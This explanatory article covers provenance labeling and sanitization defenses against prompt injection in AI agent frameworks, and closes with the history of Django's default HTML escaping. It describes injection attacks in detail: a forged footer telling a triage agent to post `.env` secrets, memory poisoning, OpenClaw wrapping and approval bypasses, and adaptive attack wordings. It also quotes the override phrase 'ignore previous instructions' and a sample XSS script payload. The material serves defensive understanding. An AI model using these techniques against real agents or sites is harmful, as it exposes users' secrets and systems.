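# Opt-in versus default-on provenance labeling in agent frameworks

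## What do opt-in and default-on provenance labeling mean?

Provenance labeling means attaching machine-readable metadata to the content an AI agent reads, so that the software around the agent can tell where each piece came from or how far to trust it. An agent is a language model run in a loop that can call tools and act on their results. Much of what it reads, such as web pages, emails and bug reports, comes from strangers, some of whom write text meant to take control of the agent. Developers usually build agents on a framework, a software library that runs the loop and passes messages between the model and its tools. The framework's designers have to decide how it treats unlabeled content. Under opt-in labeling, content counts as trusted unless a developer marks it untrusted. Under default-on labeling, outside content counts as untrusted unless someone declares it trusted. Both designs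 can use the same labels and checks, but if a developer forgets to label outside content, it is treated as trusted under opt-in labeling and untrusted under default-on labeling.

### The agent loop

A tool is a function that the surrounding application can run at the model's request, such as one that fetches a web page or sends a message. *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control* (Costa, Köpf and colleagues, 2025) describes the usual cycle. The application sends the model the conversation so far and a description of each available tool and its parameters. The model outputs either text for the user or a structured request to call a tool. If the output is a tool request, the application runs the tool, appends the result to the conversation and queries the model again. The cycle repeats until the model produces a final answer.

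Each message in the conversation has a role: system for the developer's standing instructions, user for the person's request, assistant for the model's output, and tool for results. Before every query, the application turns the whole conversation into a single string, which the model processes as one sequence of tokens (word fragments). The role markers are also tokens in that sequence. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026), a position paper by researchers from Google, NVIDIA and several universities and security firms, contrasts this with ordinary computers, where hardware lets the operating system mark a region of memory as writable or executable but not both. Language models have no equivalent barrier between instructions and data. Developers can put delimiters around outside text, and models can be trained to respect them, but persistent attackers have kept finding ways past them.

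The software developer Simon Willison (2025) explains in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents* that models are useful because they follow instructions written in ordinary language, but they cannot reliably tell from an instruction's origin whether to follow it. He coined the term "prompt injection" for attacks that exploit this weakness. The term alludes to SQL injection, an older attack in which text typed into a web form runs as a database command.

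Indirect prompt injection means planting instructions in content that an agent reads, to make it act for the attacker. *Who Is Your Agent Serving?* (2026) distinguishes this from direct prompt injection, in which the adversary is the user and types the instruction into the ordinary interface. An indirect attacker only needs to write somewhere the agent will later look, and does not need access to the agent itself. Because the loop resends the whole conversation at each step, the planted text stays in the model's input for every later decision in the run.

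### The issue-triage agent

A small agent from Microsoft's *Stop prompt injection from hijacking your agent* (2026) makes a convenient running example. It sorts the issues, meaning bug reports and requests, that people file against a software project on GitHub. It has four tools:

- `read_issue` fetches an issue;
- `read_file` reads a file from the project's repository;
- `post_comment` replies to an issue, in public if the repository is public;
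- `write_file` changes a file, for instance to correct a typo.

In Microsoft's scenario, an attacker files a plausible report about a failed build on macOS and adds a footer that looks like a system message. In the footer, the attacker claims that a maintainer has authorized access to the project's secrets and tells the agent to read `.env`, a file where developers often keep passwords and access keys, and post the contents as a reply. A person reading the issue would see a bug report with a strange ending, but the model receives it all as one continuous string. If the model takes the footer for a genuine instruction, it can post the secrets publicly with two ordinary tool calls.

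Security researchers call the two ends of such a route the source and the sink. A source is any point where content enters the agent's context, such as a tool result, a file or stored memory. A sink is a tool or output whose effect matters for security. The triage agent's sinks are `post_comment`, which can publish something private, and `write_file`, which can alter code that other people run. A tool for fetching web pages can be both source and sink. Kim, Trampert and colleagues (2026) point out in *Flowsh* that a web request discloses the requested address to the server, so the call that fetches untrusted text can also leak a secret.

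The sources include issue titles, bodies and comments, which anyone with an account can write on a public repository. Metadata is easier to overlook. *Clinejection*, by the security researcher adnanthekhan, describes a triage agent that the makers of the coding tool Cline ran until February 2026. A template pasted each issue's title and its author's account name straight into the agent's prompt, so neither passed through a tool before reaching the model. GitHub's *Script injections* lists names, email addresses and branch names among the fields that outsiders may control, and GitHub Security Lab singles out branch names and email addresses as less intuitive cases. Synacktiv's *GitHub Actions exploitation* adds the names and email addresses of commit authors, the people recorded as having made each change to the code. The advice from GitHub and Synacktiv is about conventional automation scripts,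 where such a field can end up running as a shell command, but a triage agent may well read the same fields.

The agent reads repository files through `read_file`. Maintainers may have reviewed every file, or the agent may be reading a stranger's proposed change or a file it wrote itself after reading a hostile issue.

Error messages come back to the model the same way successful results do, and they often quote the input that caused the failure. If an attacker's issue supplies a file path that `read_file` cannot find, the error may repeat the attacker's words. Kim and colleagues therefore give a command's error output the same label as its normal output. Attackers can also imitate errors. The issue title adnanthekhan used to test Cline's agent was written to look like a report from a failed tool.

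Every query's prompt includes the tool descriptions, so text by a tool's author appears next to the developer's instructions. Costa and colleagues and Kim and colleagues both assume that this text is trustworthy. That assumption is reasonable for four tools that a project's developers wrote themselves, but much less so for tools from outside servers connected through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for connecting agents to tools. Willison thinks the protocol encourages people to combine tools from different sources.

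The last item is stored memory, which Microsoft's triage agent doesn't have. But a team could easily let it keep notes on recurring bugs, and anything that got into the notes during one run would still be there in later runs. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* describes an attack through stored memory on ChatGPT's macOS app. Text in an untrusted document or website planted instructions in the app's "Memories" feature, and the app then sent the user's later conversations to the attacker's server.

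### Labels and uncovered paths

In the security usage followed here, a provenance label is a small piece of metadata that records where content came from or how far it is trusted, and that a program can inspect before it allows an action. Some research uses "provenance" more broadly. In *From Agent Traces to Trust*, Wang, Zhang and colleagues (2026) use "execution provenance" for a graph of an entire run that links documents, tool calls and memory items to the claims and actions they contributed to. They also observe that the same retrieved passage is called "evidence" in work on attribution, "context" in work on retrieval and "taint source" in security.

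An integrity label records whether an untrusted party could have influenced the content. A confidentiality label records who may see it, either as a level such as public or private or as a list of permitted readers. For example, an issue on a public repository is untrusted and public, while the `.env` file is trusted and private. The integrity label doesn't depend on intent, so an honest bug report from a stranger gets the same label as a malicious one. This makes the label coarse, but it works without anyone having to recognize an attack.

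Content seldom reaches a sink in its original form, because the model summarizes, quotes and recombines what it reads. Label propagation computes a label for derived content from the labels of its inputs, so a summary of an untrusted issue is also untrusted. Many designs also keep a context label, which combines the labels of everything the model has read so far in a run, with the most restrictive input prevailing. Once the triage agent has read the hostile issue and then `.env`, its context is both untrusted and private, and a check at `post_comment` can refuse for either reason.

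Some work requires exceptions. Endorsement means deliberately raising content from untrusted to trusted for a stated purpose. For example, a maintainer might read an issue and approve its wording for use in one correction to the documentation. A trust override is an explicit declaration that exempts content or a tool from the default treatment, such as a configuration line that treats all issues from project members as trusted. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* cautions that authentication establishes who sent something, but a known sender can still pass on harmful text. This caution applies to overrides based on who the sender is.

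An uncovered path is a route from an untrusted source to a sink along which no label or check applies. Even a careful design can have one, as Cline's template shows. If the framework had labeled every tool result, the issue title would still have reached the model unlabeled, because it was not a tool result. In per-call sanitization, a developer makes an explicit call to clean, wrap or screen untrusted text at each place where it enters. Omitting any of these calls leaves an uncovered path.

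### Three separate defaults

Microsoft's *Information-flow control* breaks the method into three steps: label the data, propagate the labels, and check them before acting. Each step has its own default, and a claim that a framework is "secure by default" may refer to only one step.

| Question | Opt-in answer | Default-on answer | What the triage agent's developer can forget under opt-in |
|---|---|---|---|
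| What does a missing label mean? | Trusted | Untrusted | Labeling the output of `read_issue` |
| Do labels propagate? | Only where a developer's code copies them | Automatically | Copying the issue's label to a summary of it |
| Do sinks check labels? | Only if the sink declares a rule | Always, unless someone declares an exemption | Declaring a rule on `post_comment` |

A framework can also record a missing label as unknown. This separates content that somebody judged untrusted from content that nobody judged, which helps auditors find gaps. But when the model requests a sink, the framework still has to run it, refuse it or ask a person. If the framework runs the sink on unknown content without asking, the design is opt-in in practice.

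A framework can turn on some of the three settings by default and leave others opt-in. For example, it might treat unlabeled results as untrusted and propagate labels automatically, but check labels at sinks only where a developer has declared a rule. Suppose the developer declares a rule for `write_file` but overlooks `post_comment`. When the agent reads the hostile issue, the context label correctly changes to untrusted, but the agent still posts the comment because no rule makes `post_comment` check the label.

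In the reverse arrangement, every sink refuses untrusted context by default, but text without a label counts as trusted. The developer labels issue bodies but forgets that a template also puts the author's name into the prompt. An instruction hidden in the name field is therefore treated as trusted. The check at `write_file` runs but detects no untrusted text, so the call proceeds.

Propagation can fail even when both of the other defaults are strict. Suppose the developer has declared the output of `read_file` trusted because maintainers review the repository. The agent summarizes a hostile issue and asks to save the summary in a notes file, and a busy maintainer approves. If the file does not keep the issue's label, the next run reads the attacker's instructions as trusted content. Kim and colleagues store labels with the files so that later sessions inherit the restrictions.

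Real products also mix the settings. According to Microsoft's May 2026 post, the framework treats the output of an unlabeled tool as trusted, but in later documentation for the same framework, the default is untrusted. In both versions, a developer has to switch on the security module first.

### Fail-safe defaults and complete mediation

The case for default-on labeling rests on two design principles, fail-safe defaults and complete mediation. The computer scientists Jerome Saltzer and Michael Schroeder published both in 1975, among eight principles for protecting information in shared computers.

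Under fail-safe defaults, an idea Saltzer and Schroeder credited to E. Glaser in 1965, a system denies access unless stated conditions are met. They argued that this makes mistakes easier to notice. A faulty mechanism for granting permission tends to refuse legitimate requests, which people notice quickly, whereas a faulty mechanism for listing prohibitions tends to allow requests it should block, which may go unnoticed in normal use.

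For an agent framework, the principle would determine two of the three defaults. Content without a label would be untrusted, and a sink with no declared rule would refuse to run in untrusted context. Content would also count as untrusted if the framework could not parse its label or lost the label while shortening a long conversation. If a developer added a new tool to the triage agent and forgot to classify it, `post_comment` would be blocked as soon as the agent had used that tool, and the developer would look for the cause. With opt-in labeling, the same mistake has no visible effect until somebody exploits it.

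Complete mediation requires a check on every access to every object, including during startup, recovery and maintenance. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* applies this principle to agents. A reference monitor, the component that permits or rejects actions under the security policy, must intercept every request, with no way to bypass it. To meet this requirement, a framework would have to label all content that enters it, including prompt templates, error messages, tool descriptions, memory and any saved conversation that the agent resumes. It would also have to propagate labels automatically, since a check is of little use if the label has already been lost.

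It would also have to check every route to an effect, which is the harder of the two requirements. If `write_file` can change the configuration of the project's automated build, the build may later publish content that `post_comment` would have blocked. The paper attributes this difficulty to agents turning a broad request directly into low-level actions through shells, programming interfaces and web pages, which leaves no single natural place to enforce a rule such as "do not share sensitive data".

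Saltzer and Schroeder drew two further requirements from complete mediation. The first is a reliable way to identify the source of each request. In an agent, every tool call comes from the same model, no matter whose text prompted it, so the caller's identity is uninformative and the context label has to replace it. The second is suspicion of any shortcut that remembers the result of an earlier check. A maintainer who clicks "always allow" for `post_comment` at the start of a run makes that choice before the agent opens the hostile issue, so a framework that followed the principle would request approval again once the context label changed.

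## How does sanitizing each call work, and where does it leave gaps?

To protect the issue-triage agent this way, a developer would need a separate sanitizing call for the output of `read_issue`, any title or author name that a template inserts, error messages, and so on. Someone can easily leave out a call, and security advisories for OpenClaw, a popular open-source agent framework, document many such omissions. Even when every call is in place, the model may read the warning and still obey the planted instruction. Experiments with determined attackers measure how often this happens.

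### What each method changes in the prompt

The simplest method puts a warning before outside text and a pair of markers around it. OpenClaw does this with a function called `wrapExternalContent`, which Mint Security's *When AI Agents Browse Unprotected* examines. The function first adds a security notice telling the model that the text comes from an external, untrusted source and that no part of it is a system instruction. The notice also lists requests to ignore, such as deleting files, revealing sensitive information or messaging third parties. The function then adds an opening marker, a few lines giving the source, sender and subject, the text itself, and a closing marker. It doesn't remove any of the attacker's words from the prompt, so the model can still read them.

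An attacker who knows the closing marker can type it into a bug report, so that the text after it appears to be outside the untrusted block. OpenClaw therefore replaces any copy of its own markers that it finds in the text. It first converts full-width Unicode characters, which look like ordinary letters and angle brackets, to their plain forms. Mint Security found that the search matched only markers with exactly three angle brackets, so a forged marker with two got through. An ordinary parser would also miss the forgery, but a language model doesn't need an exact match and may treat it as a real marker. Web developers escape HTML by replacing an angle bracket with a code that browsers display as a bracket but never interpret as markup, and no such code exists for language models.

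Other methods make the boundary harder to miss or to forge. Prompt sandwiching repeats the user's request after the untrusted text to keep the model focused on it. Spotlighting, which Keegan Hines and colleagues proposed in 2024, has three versions. Delimiting separates trusted from untrusted text with special tokens and explains them to the model. Datamarking inserts a chosen character throughout the untrusted text, for example in place of every space, so that even a fragment from the middle is marked. Encoding converts the text to a scheme such as Base64, which makes it look like a meaningless string of letters and digits. A capable model can decode the string, but decoding also recovers any instructions the attacker put in the text.

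Removal deletes or replaces part of the text, and it works best when the danger lies in particular characters. For example, some servers for self-hosted models convert the typed-out form of a role marker into the real token, so a web page containing that text could forge a system message. OpenClaw strips these strings from wrapped content, according to its *Prompt injection* documentation page. No comparable list of strings exists for harmful requests written in ordinary sentences.

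Screening uses a separate program to check whether the text looks like an attack. If the text passes, the main model receives it unchanged. If it fails, the application typically blocks it or returns a stock refusal. Many screens are small language models trained on both harmless prompts and known attacks. OpenClaw has a cruder screen that checks the text against a list of phrases such as "ignore previous instructions". In the version Mint Security audited, this screen only logged matches and still passed the text to the model.

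Two research systems screen text by running a model on it and checking how the model behaves. Data Sentinel asks a detector model to repeat a secret key while ignoring the suspect text, and flags the text if the model fails to repeat the key. MELON runs the agent a second time, replacing the user's request with a harmless request to summarize the tool results. If the agent makes the same tool call in both runs, the tool results probably prompted the call rather than the user's request.

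### Where OpenClaw left out the call

OpenClaw runs on a person's own computer and connects a language model to messaging apps, files, a browser and the command line. It had more than 194,000 stars on GitHub, a rough measure of popularity, by mid-February 2026. Mint Security searched the code of version 2026.2.9 for every use of the wrapping functions, and the results were mixed.

| Path into the prompt | Wrapped in version 2026.2.9? |
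|---|---|
| Pages fetched with the `web_fetch` tool | Yes |
| Web search through Perplexity or Brave | Yes |
| Web search through Grok | No |
| Gmail and webhook messages | Yes |
| Metadata of chat channels | Yes |
| Output of shell commands | No |
| Skill files (instructions that teach the agent a task) | No |
| Opening message of a scheduled job | No |

The Grok entry is a clear case of a forgotten call. One source file handled all three search providers, but it wrapped the results only for the other two. Version 2026.2.12 added the missing call for Grok.

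The shell gap was wider, and Mint Security demonstrated it with Moltbook, a social network where AI agents post and people can only watch. An agent joins by reading a skill file with instructions to check its feed every 30 minutes using `curl`, a command-line program for downloading web pages. The posts therefore arrived as shell output, without a notice or markers. If the instructions had specified `web_fetch` for the same address, OpenClaw would have wrapped every post. Protection for the same text thus depended on which tool the skill's writer chose. Mint Security cites research that found hidden injections in about 2.6% of Moltbook posts.

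Scheduled jobs went unwrapped for a different reason. The code that wrapped incoming messages first checked whether a session's name began with `hook:`, the prefix for emails and webhooks. The regular Moltbook check ran under a name beginning with `cron:`, so OpenClaw treated its opening message as internal. OpenClaw wrapped messages by default only in the sessions its developers had listed, and trusted the rest.

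OpenClaw's approval system was set to deny shell commands unless a user had allowed them, but the code applied that rule on only two of the three routes by which a command could run. The developers designed the third route for commands inside a Docker container, an isolated environment that would limit any damage. That route was the default, but the container was off by default, so with the standard settings, commands ran directly on the user's machine without the approval check.

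Mint Security recommends wrapping shell output whenever the command makes a network request, as `curl` and `wget` do. That would close the Moltbook path, but the framework would have to recognize such commands. *A Security Analysis of the OpenClaw AI Agent Framework* (Suwansathit, Zhang and Gu, 2026) describes a similar problem in the approval system, which identified commands from their text and which researchers bypassed in three unrelated ways. One used `busybox`, a single program that contains many smaller ones, including a shell. A user who approved `busybox` for one shell command had in effect approved any later shell command run through it. A list of downloading programs would have the same weakness, since a few lines of Python can fetch a web page. Wrapping all shell output would be safer, but it would put warnings around a lot of harmless text.

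Skill files are harder to sanitize because the agent is supposed to follow them, so a notice telling the model to ignore their instructions would make them useless. Suwansathit and colleagues describe a skill named "yahoofinance" that did nothing with financial data and told users to install an attacker's program as a prerequisite. OpenClaw gave that text the same authority as instructions from the agent's owner. Sanitizing cannot replace a developer's decision about whether to trust a skill at all.

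### Text that did not look like input

Some omitted calls involve text that few developers would think of as input. OSV's *OpenClaw* (2026), an entry in a public vulnerability database, reports that the framework inserted its current working directory's path into the system prompt without sanitizing it. A folder name can contain line breaks and invisible formatting characters, so an attacker who got OpenClaw to run inside such a folder could use the name to break up the prompt and add instructions. The entry rates the flaw's severity at 8.6 out of 10. As with the issue title in Cline's template, the text never passed through a tool, so even a rule that wrapped every tool result would have missed it.

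Version 2026.2.15 strips control characters, formatting characters and line separators from the path. It leaves ordinary words in a folder name, but without line breaks they are harder to disguise as a separate section of the prompt.

In another case, the vulnerability was in OpenClaw's own code. GitLab's *OpenClaw Vulnerable to Local File Exfiltration via MCP Tool Result* (2026) explains that the framework searched tool results for directives beginning with `MEDIA:` and treated the rest as the path of a file to deliver to a chat app such as Slack or WhatsApp. It did not check which tool had supplied the directive, so a malicious tool server could have files sent from the user's computer. OpenClaw did check file locations, but it allowed the system's temporary folder by default. A warning in the prompt would not have helped, because the attack did not need to fool the model. The developers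 fixed this in version 2026.2.21.

Suwansathit and colleagues classified 470 security advisories that researchers filed against OpenClaw between January 31 and April 15, 2026, up from 190 in their February count. In their analysis, the recurring cause is that OpenClaw handled trust decisions separately in each part of the program, often at each individual call, with no common rule.

The paper's clearest example is the code that connects OpenClaw to chat services. Developers wrote a separate connection for each of 15 services, and every connection had to check whether a sender was on the owner's approved list. Thirteen advisories describe connections that checked the list against names senders could change. On Nextcloud Talk, anyone could rename their account "alice" and pass a check meant for the real Alice. The services also supply permanent identifiers, and the paper argues that one shared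 function using them would have prevented all 13 flaws.

In four other advisories, outside text reached the prompt as if it were harmless information. It came from Slack channel metadata, error log headers, linked resource names and parts of file paths. Mint Security found that the channel metadata was wrapped by version 2026.2.9. Only 11 of the 470 advisories fall under the study's category for the agent's context window, so the study is mainly evidence about scattered security checks in general. It is still relevant because wrapping depends on the same kind of local decision.

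OpenClaw lets one agent session send a message to another, and it used to store that message as though a person had typed it. An attacker who controlled one session could therefore give orders to another. The repair for this flaw goes beyond sanitizing text by recording whether each message came from an outside user, another session or the system itself. Suwansathit and colleagues propose requiring such a tag on every string that enters the prompt, so that the framework can consider an instruction's origin when it authorizes a tool call.

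OpenClaw has since extended its protection. Its September 2026 documentation describes wrapping for uploaded text files and text extracted from attached documents. When the container is off, commands now go by default to one of the two routes where Mint Security had found that the approval rules were enforced, and an explicit request for a missing container fails. But the container is still opt-in. The documentation lists fetch tools, read tools and incoming chat messages among the content that the wrapping layer cleans but doesn't mention shell output, so the largest gap that Mint Security found in its audit may still be open.

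Even a complete set of sanitizing calls would protect text only as it first arrives. The wrapper can get lost in the triage agent's notes file, just as a label can, because the model may summarize the attacker's request without copying the notice or markers. The code that later reads the file then needs its own sanitizing call.

### When the model obeys wrapped text

Until recently, researchers usually tested sanitizing methods against a fixed set of known attacks. Nasr, Carlini and colleagues (2025) argued in *The Attacker Moves Second* that this is misleading, because a real attacker can study a defense and adjust. They tested 12 published defenses against attackers who did so. Some targeted prompt injection, and others targeted jailbreaks, in which users themselves try to get forbidden answers.

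All the attacks repeated the same loop of proposing candidate texts, scoring how close each one came to working, and using the most promising ones to produce the next batch. The researchers ran this loop in four ways. One used the model's gradients, another used reinforcement learning to train a language model to write better attacks, a third had a language model mutate the best texts in a genetic search, and the fourth was a public competition with more than 500 people.

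Spotlighting and prompt sandwiching did very well against the fixed attacks in AgentDojo, a standard test for agents, where as few as 1% of attacks succeeded. The genetic search raised the success rate above 95% against both. People found 265 successful attacks on spotlighting and 178 on sandwiching. Screening did only slightly better. Three commercial or open classifiers let through more than 90% of the adaptive attacks, and a fourth, PIGuard, let through 71%. The search beat MELON 76% of the time when it used no details of how MELON works, and 95% of the time when it used full details. With full details, the attack told any system that was merely summarizing the file to ignore the instructions, so the suspicious tool call never appeared in MELON's second run.

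One attack that beat sandwiching looked like a notice from an access-control system. It listed steps for a credential check supposedly required to write to a channel, starting with inviting an outsider to the company's Slack workspace. Repeating the user's request afterward did not help, because the attack looked like a step toward fulfilling that request. OpenClaw's notice leaves room for a similar attack, because it forbids running commands mentioned in the content "unless explicitly appropriate for the user's actual request", and an attacker can try to make a command look appropriate.

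An even shorter text got past one of the classifiers. It mentioned a company policy requiring anyone who rescheduled a meeting to delete a certain tracking file. Legitimate office emails often read much the same way, so a classifier strict enough to catch this text would also block many of them. Nasr and colleagues found that the classifiers already raised more false alarms than the other defenses.

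These percentages do not predict how often attacks succeed in daily use, because the researchers gave their attackers ample computing power and, for the classifiers, the detector's confidence score after each attempt. The figures also cannot be used to rank the defenses, because the researchers tested them with different procedures. The experiment does show that a near-zero success rate for known attacks is weak evidence of how a defense will perform against an attacker who keeps trying. The same caution applies to the low rates that developers now publish for newer models.

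### How often models followed injected instructions in 2026

Model developers have meanwhile trained their models to resist planted instructions, and test results have improved a great deal. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin et al., 2026) reported in March on a large public competition in which 464 participants made about 272,000 attack attempts against 13 models. The 41 scenarios ranged from email assistants to coding agents. In most of them, an attack counted only if the agent carried out the harmful action and hid it from the user in its final reply. Success rates ran from 0.5% of attempts for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% for Gemini 2.5 Pro.

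The participants could see the conversation and knew exactly which tool call they had to trigger, advantages that real attackers often would not have. Dziemian and colleagues therefore regard the results as an upper bound for single-turn attacks of this kind. However, the rates count every attempt, including those of beginners. Successes also accumulated steadily throughout the competition, with no sign that attackers were running out of ideas.

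OpenAI tested GPT-Red, a model it had trained to attack other models, in a copy of this competition's environment. Against GPT-5.1, GPT-Red found a successful attack in 84% of the scenarios, compared with 13% for human attackers. These are per-scenario rates, so they are not comparable with the per-attempt rates above.

OpenAI then used GPT-Red's attacks to train its newer models. TechRepublic's *OpenAI’s GPT-5.6 Tests Show Prompt-Injection Gains and Agent Risks* (2026) reports that GPT-5.6 Sol failed on about 0.05% of attacks typed directly into the chat but on 3.77% of indirect attacks, which are hidden in tool results and other outside content. A month later, OpenAI's *GPT-6 Astra System Card* (2026) reported that the defender succeeded against 99.79% of indirect attacks, up from 96.23%, so the failure rate fell to 0.21%, about one eighteenth of the earlier figure. OpenAI measured this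 improvement with the same family of automated attacks that it used in training, and a different kind of attacker might do better.

The 0.21% rate is per attempt, so an attacker who made 200 independent attempts would have roughly a 34% chance of succeeding at least once. Real attempts are not independent, since some targets block every attack and others fail repeatedly, but an attacker who can file issues or send emails for free has little reason to stop at one. According to VentureBeat, the attack success rates Anthropic published for Claude Opus 4.6 ranged from 0% to 78.6%, depending on where the agent worked and how many attempts the attacker made. The highest rate was for 200 attempts without additional safeguards, and it fell to 57.1% with them.

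Attack success rates depend as much on the test conditions as on the model. VentureBeat reports that attacks on a browser agent using the later Opus 4.8 succeeded in 31.5% of attempts before safeguards. The attacker adapted to the model's behavior in 129 test environments. VentureBeat warns against comparing this rate with OpenAI's robustness scores, which came from known attacks on one type of input. *INFUSE* (2026), a benchmark published in October, found that on average 19.6% of attack runs compromised undefended agents when a language model judged the results, and 15.4% when a simpler automatic check did. But its average includes older and smaller models such as GPT-4o-mini, so it reflects the range of models developers might choose more than the best ones.

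Resistance to injections also doesn't always improve from one release to the next. VentureBeat reports that OpenAI's robustness score fell from 0.998 for GPT-5.4-thinking to 0.963 for GPT-5.5. Simula's *CAISS analysis of Anthropics system card for Fable 5 and Mythos 5* similarly finds that Mythos 5 and its safeguards had become less effective at blocking injections. A team that relies on the model to respect its wrappers therefore has to retest whenever it changes models.

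### Why developers still sanitize

Wrapping adds only a few lines of text to the prompt and needs no second model, and a developer can introduce it in an afternoon without redesigning any tools. A classifier takes more compute because it has to run on each piece of text, but it requires no change to the main model.

These methods also let the agent keep doing its job. The triage agent can read a wrapped issue, look up the relevant file and post a reply in the same run. A rule that blocked `post_comment` after the agent read any text from a stranger would stop the attack in the running example, but it would also stop most of the agent's useful replies.

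Many attacks are unsophisticated. Someone might plant the same sentence on a thousand web pages without optimizing it against any one company's agent. Fixed attacks succeeded 1% of the time against spotlighting and sandwiching, which is reasonable evidence that these defenses help in such cases. Nasr and colleagues likewise call classifiers useful, though limited, because they can block some opportunistic attacks. The safeguards on Opus 4.6 also stopped some attacks even after 200 attempts, though more than half still succeeded.

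Willison (2026) describes a public challenge in which people sent about 6,000 hostile emails to an assistant running on Opus 4.6. The assistant's prompt included rules against revealing credentials or running commands because of anything in an email. All the attempts failed. The test cannot separate the effect of the rules from that of the model's training, but the combination clearly made attacks difficult. Willison still advises against deploying an agent where a successful injection could do irreversible damage, because 6,000 failures do not guarantee that the next attacker will fail. OpenClaw's documentation similarly recommends choosing a resistant model as the easiest layer of protection and keeping hard limits on tools for anything the owner must not lose.

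Sanitizing can also help where a check on tool calls has nothing to block. For example, a hostile issue might lead the triage agent to describe a serious security bug as trivial. A rule about sinks might never apply, because the agent would send no secret and change no file, but the summary would mislead a maintainer who trusted it. A warning around the issue could make the model less likely to accept the claim.

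## What happened when web templates began to escape by default?

Long before anyone built agents, web developers had to sanitize each piece of text from strangers with a separate call before putting it into a page, and they kept forgetting some of the calls. From 2007 onward, some frameworks made templates sanitize every value unless a developer exempted it. Their experience is useful evidence about what a safer default can do, although web pages have one advantage that agents lack.

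### Cross-site scripting and HTML escaping

A web template is a page with gaps that a program fills in when someone visits. Suppose the project in the running example also has a web page that shows its latest issue:

```
<h2>{{ title }}</h2>
<p>Reported by <a href="{{ website }}">{{ name }}</a></p>
```

The project's developers wrote the HTML tags, but whoever files the issue chooses the values in double braces. An attacker could file one titled `<script>stealLogin()</script>`. If the template copies that title unchanged, every visitor's browser runs the script as if it were the project's own code. This is cross-site scripting, or XSS. *DjangoChecker* (Steinhauser and Tůma, 2019) lists stolen credentials, hijacked sessions and recorded keystrokes among the possible results of XSS.

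HTML escaping prevents this by replacing characters with special meaning in HTML with harmless codes. For example, `<` becomes `&lt;` and a double quotation mark becomes `&quot;`. Visitors see an odd title, but no code runs.

In 2006, Django, a Python web framework, escaped a value only if the template's author marked it, as in `{{ title|escape }}`. With this per-call sanitization, one missing `|escape` was enough to create a vulnerability.

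### Django's argument over the default

In *Proposal*, SmileyChris (2006) suggested on Django's mailing list that the framework escape every value by default. He argued that nearly all templates produce HTML, most values in them need escaping, and developers will miss some. Supporters included Simon Willison, who pointed out that even experienced programmers who fully understood XSS would sometimes forget the escape filter.

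The most practical objection came from Jacob Kaplan-Moss, one of Django's leaders, who opposed the change because it would break every existing template. A page that deliberately inserted HTML would show the tags to visitors. Text that a program had already escaped would be escaped again, so visitors would see `&lt;` instead of `<`.

Other developers objected on principle. Python programmers have a maxim that explicit is better than implicit, and several people did not want a framework changing their data without their knowledge. They remembered "magic quotes", a PHP feature that altered incoming data automatically. Willison agreed that magic quotes had been a disaster, but he blamed the global setting that turned them on or off. A component written for one setting broke under the other, which made sharing code almost impossible, so he wanted each template to control its own escaping. Another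 developer, Rowan Kerr, added that magic quotes had altered data no matter where it was going, whereas a template would escape it only on final output.

Derek Anderson's objection has held up best. He noted that SQL, HTML and JavaScript each need a different kind of escaping, and he feared that automating one of them would create a false sense of security. Phil Powell was stricter and said that developers who forgot to escape should be more careful.

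Kaplan-Moss preferred a compromise, a pair of tags that would turn on escaping for everything between them. Gábor Farkas replied that people who forgot the filter would forget the tags too, an objection that applies to any opt-in protection, however convenient. Gary Wilson asked whether the project would rather hear from users who couldn't turn escaping off or from users whose sites had been hacked. Saltzer and Schroeder had made much the same case for fail-safe defaults.

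In *Auto-escaping patch*, Tredinnick (2006) kept the first working version opt-in because another of Django's leaders preferred it that way. Speed was not much of an obstacle, since the extra checks slowed a set of template tests by 0.6% with escaping switched off, barely more than the normal variation between runs.

Opinion had shifted by the following spring. Bennett (2007), in *Escaping in templates*, still disliked automatic escaping and expected to turn it off in his own work, but he now supported making it the default. He compared the existing design to pointing a gun at a developer's foot and advising them not to pull the trigger. Michael Radziej, who had used the patch in development for about two months, observed that double escaping is ugly but harmless, while a missed escape may let an attacker in.

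Django adopted escaping by default on November 14, 2007. The timing helped because Django had not yet reached version 1.0 and promised no backward compatibility before then. Django's *AutoEscaping proposal* had warned that the decision could not wait past that release.

### Marking text that is already safe

A template that escapes by default needs a way to identify strings it should leave unchanged. Django's `markdown` filter, for instance, turns plain text into HTML, and escaping that HTML would ruin the formatting. Tredinnick's patch therefore gave strings a trust label. The template treats ordinary strings as unsafe and escapes them, but copies strings returned by `mark_safe` unchanged. The standard filters that produce HTML mark their own output, so most template authors never need to think about the label.

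The same label solved most of the double-escaping problem. Tredinnick changed the old `escape` filter to skip strings already marked safe, so authors did not have to remove the filter from all their templates.

Tredinnick also needed a rule for whether a string stays marked safe after a filter changes it. Changing a safe string to lowercase leaves it safe, but deleting every `&` does not, because that damages the escape codes. In the patch, a filter's author can declare that the filter always returns safe output for safe input. Without that declaration, Django drops the safe mark and escapes the result, so forgetting the declaration leads to too much escaping rather than too little.

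Ruby on Rails, the main framework for Ruby, copied Django's automatic escaping. In *On-By-Default XSS escaping*, Koziarski (2009) planned to bring "django-style auto-escaping" to Rails 3 and warned that it could break practically every existing application. He also offered it as a plugin for the previous version so developers could try it before upgrading. According to Intertwingly's *XSS Protection by Default in Rails 3.0* (2009), the old escaping helper, `h`, remained available but did essentially nothing.

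*SafeBuffers and Rails 3.0* (Katz, 2010) explains that Rails collects a page's output in a special kind of string called a `SafeBuffer`, which escapes any ordinary string that a template adds to it and accepts other `SafeBuffer` strings unchanged. The HTML that a developer typed into the template goes in without a check, so the protection adds no overhead for those parts of the page.

Ruby could already label strings from outside as "tainted", but Rails did not base its escaping on those labels. A contributor to *On-By-Default XSS escaping* explained that database drivers, the components that fetch stored data, were inconsistent about tainting the strings they returned. A missing taint mark could therefore mean that a string was trustworthy or that a driver's author had never added one. Rails removed this ambiguity by treating every string as untrusted until someone marked it safe. Unlabeled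 tool results in agent frameworks are ambiguous in the same way.

### Jinja2 kept escaping off

Unlike Django, the Python template system Jinja2 left automatic escaping off by default. Its author, Armin Ronacher, had joined Django's debate in 2007 to argue against automatic escaping, which he had found painful to add to an earlier version of Jinja. His main trouble was that a filter could join a marked string to an ordinary one and lose the mark. After reading Django's code, he objected less, as long as users could turn the feature off. Jinja2 offered automatic escaping as an option when Willison noted its release in July 2008.

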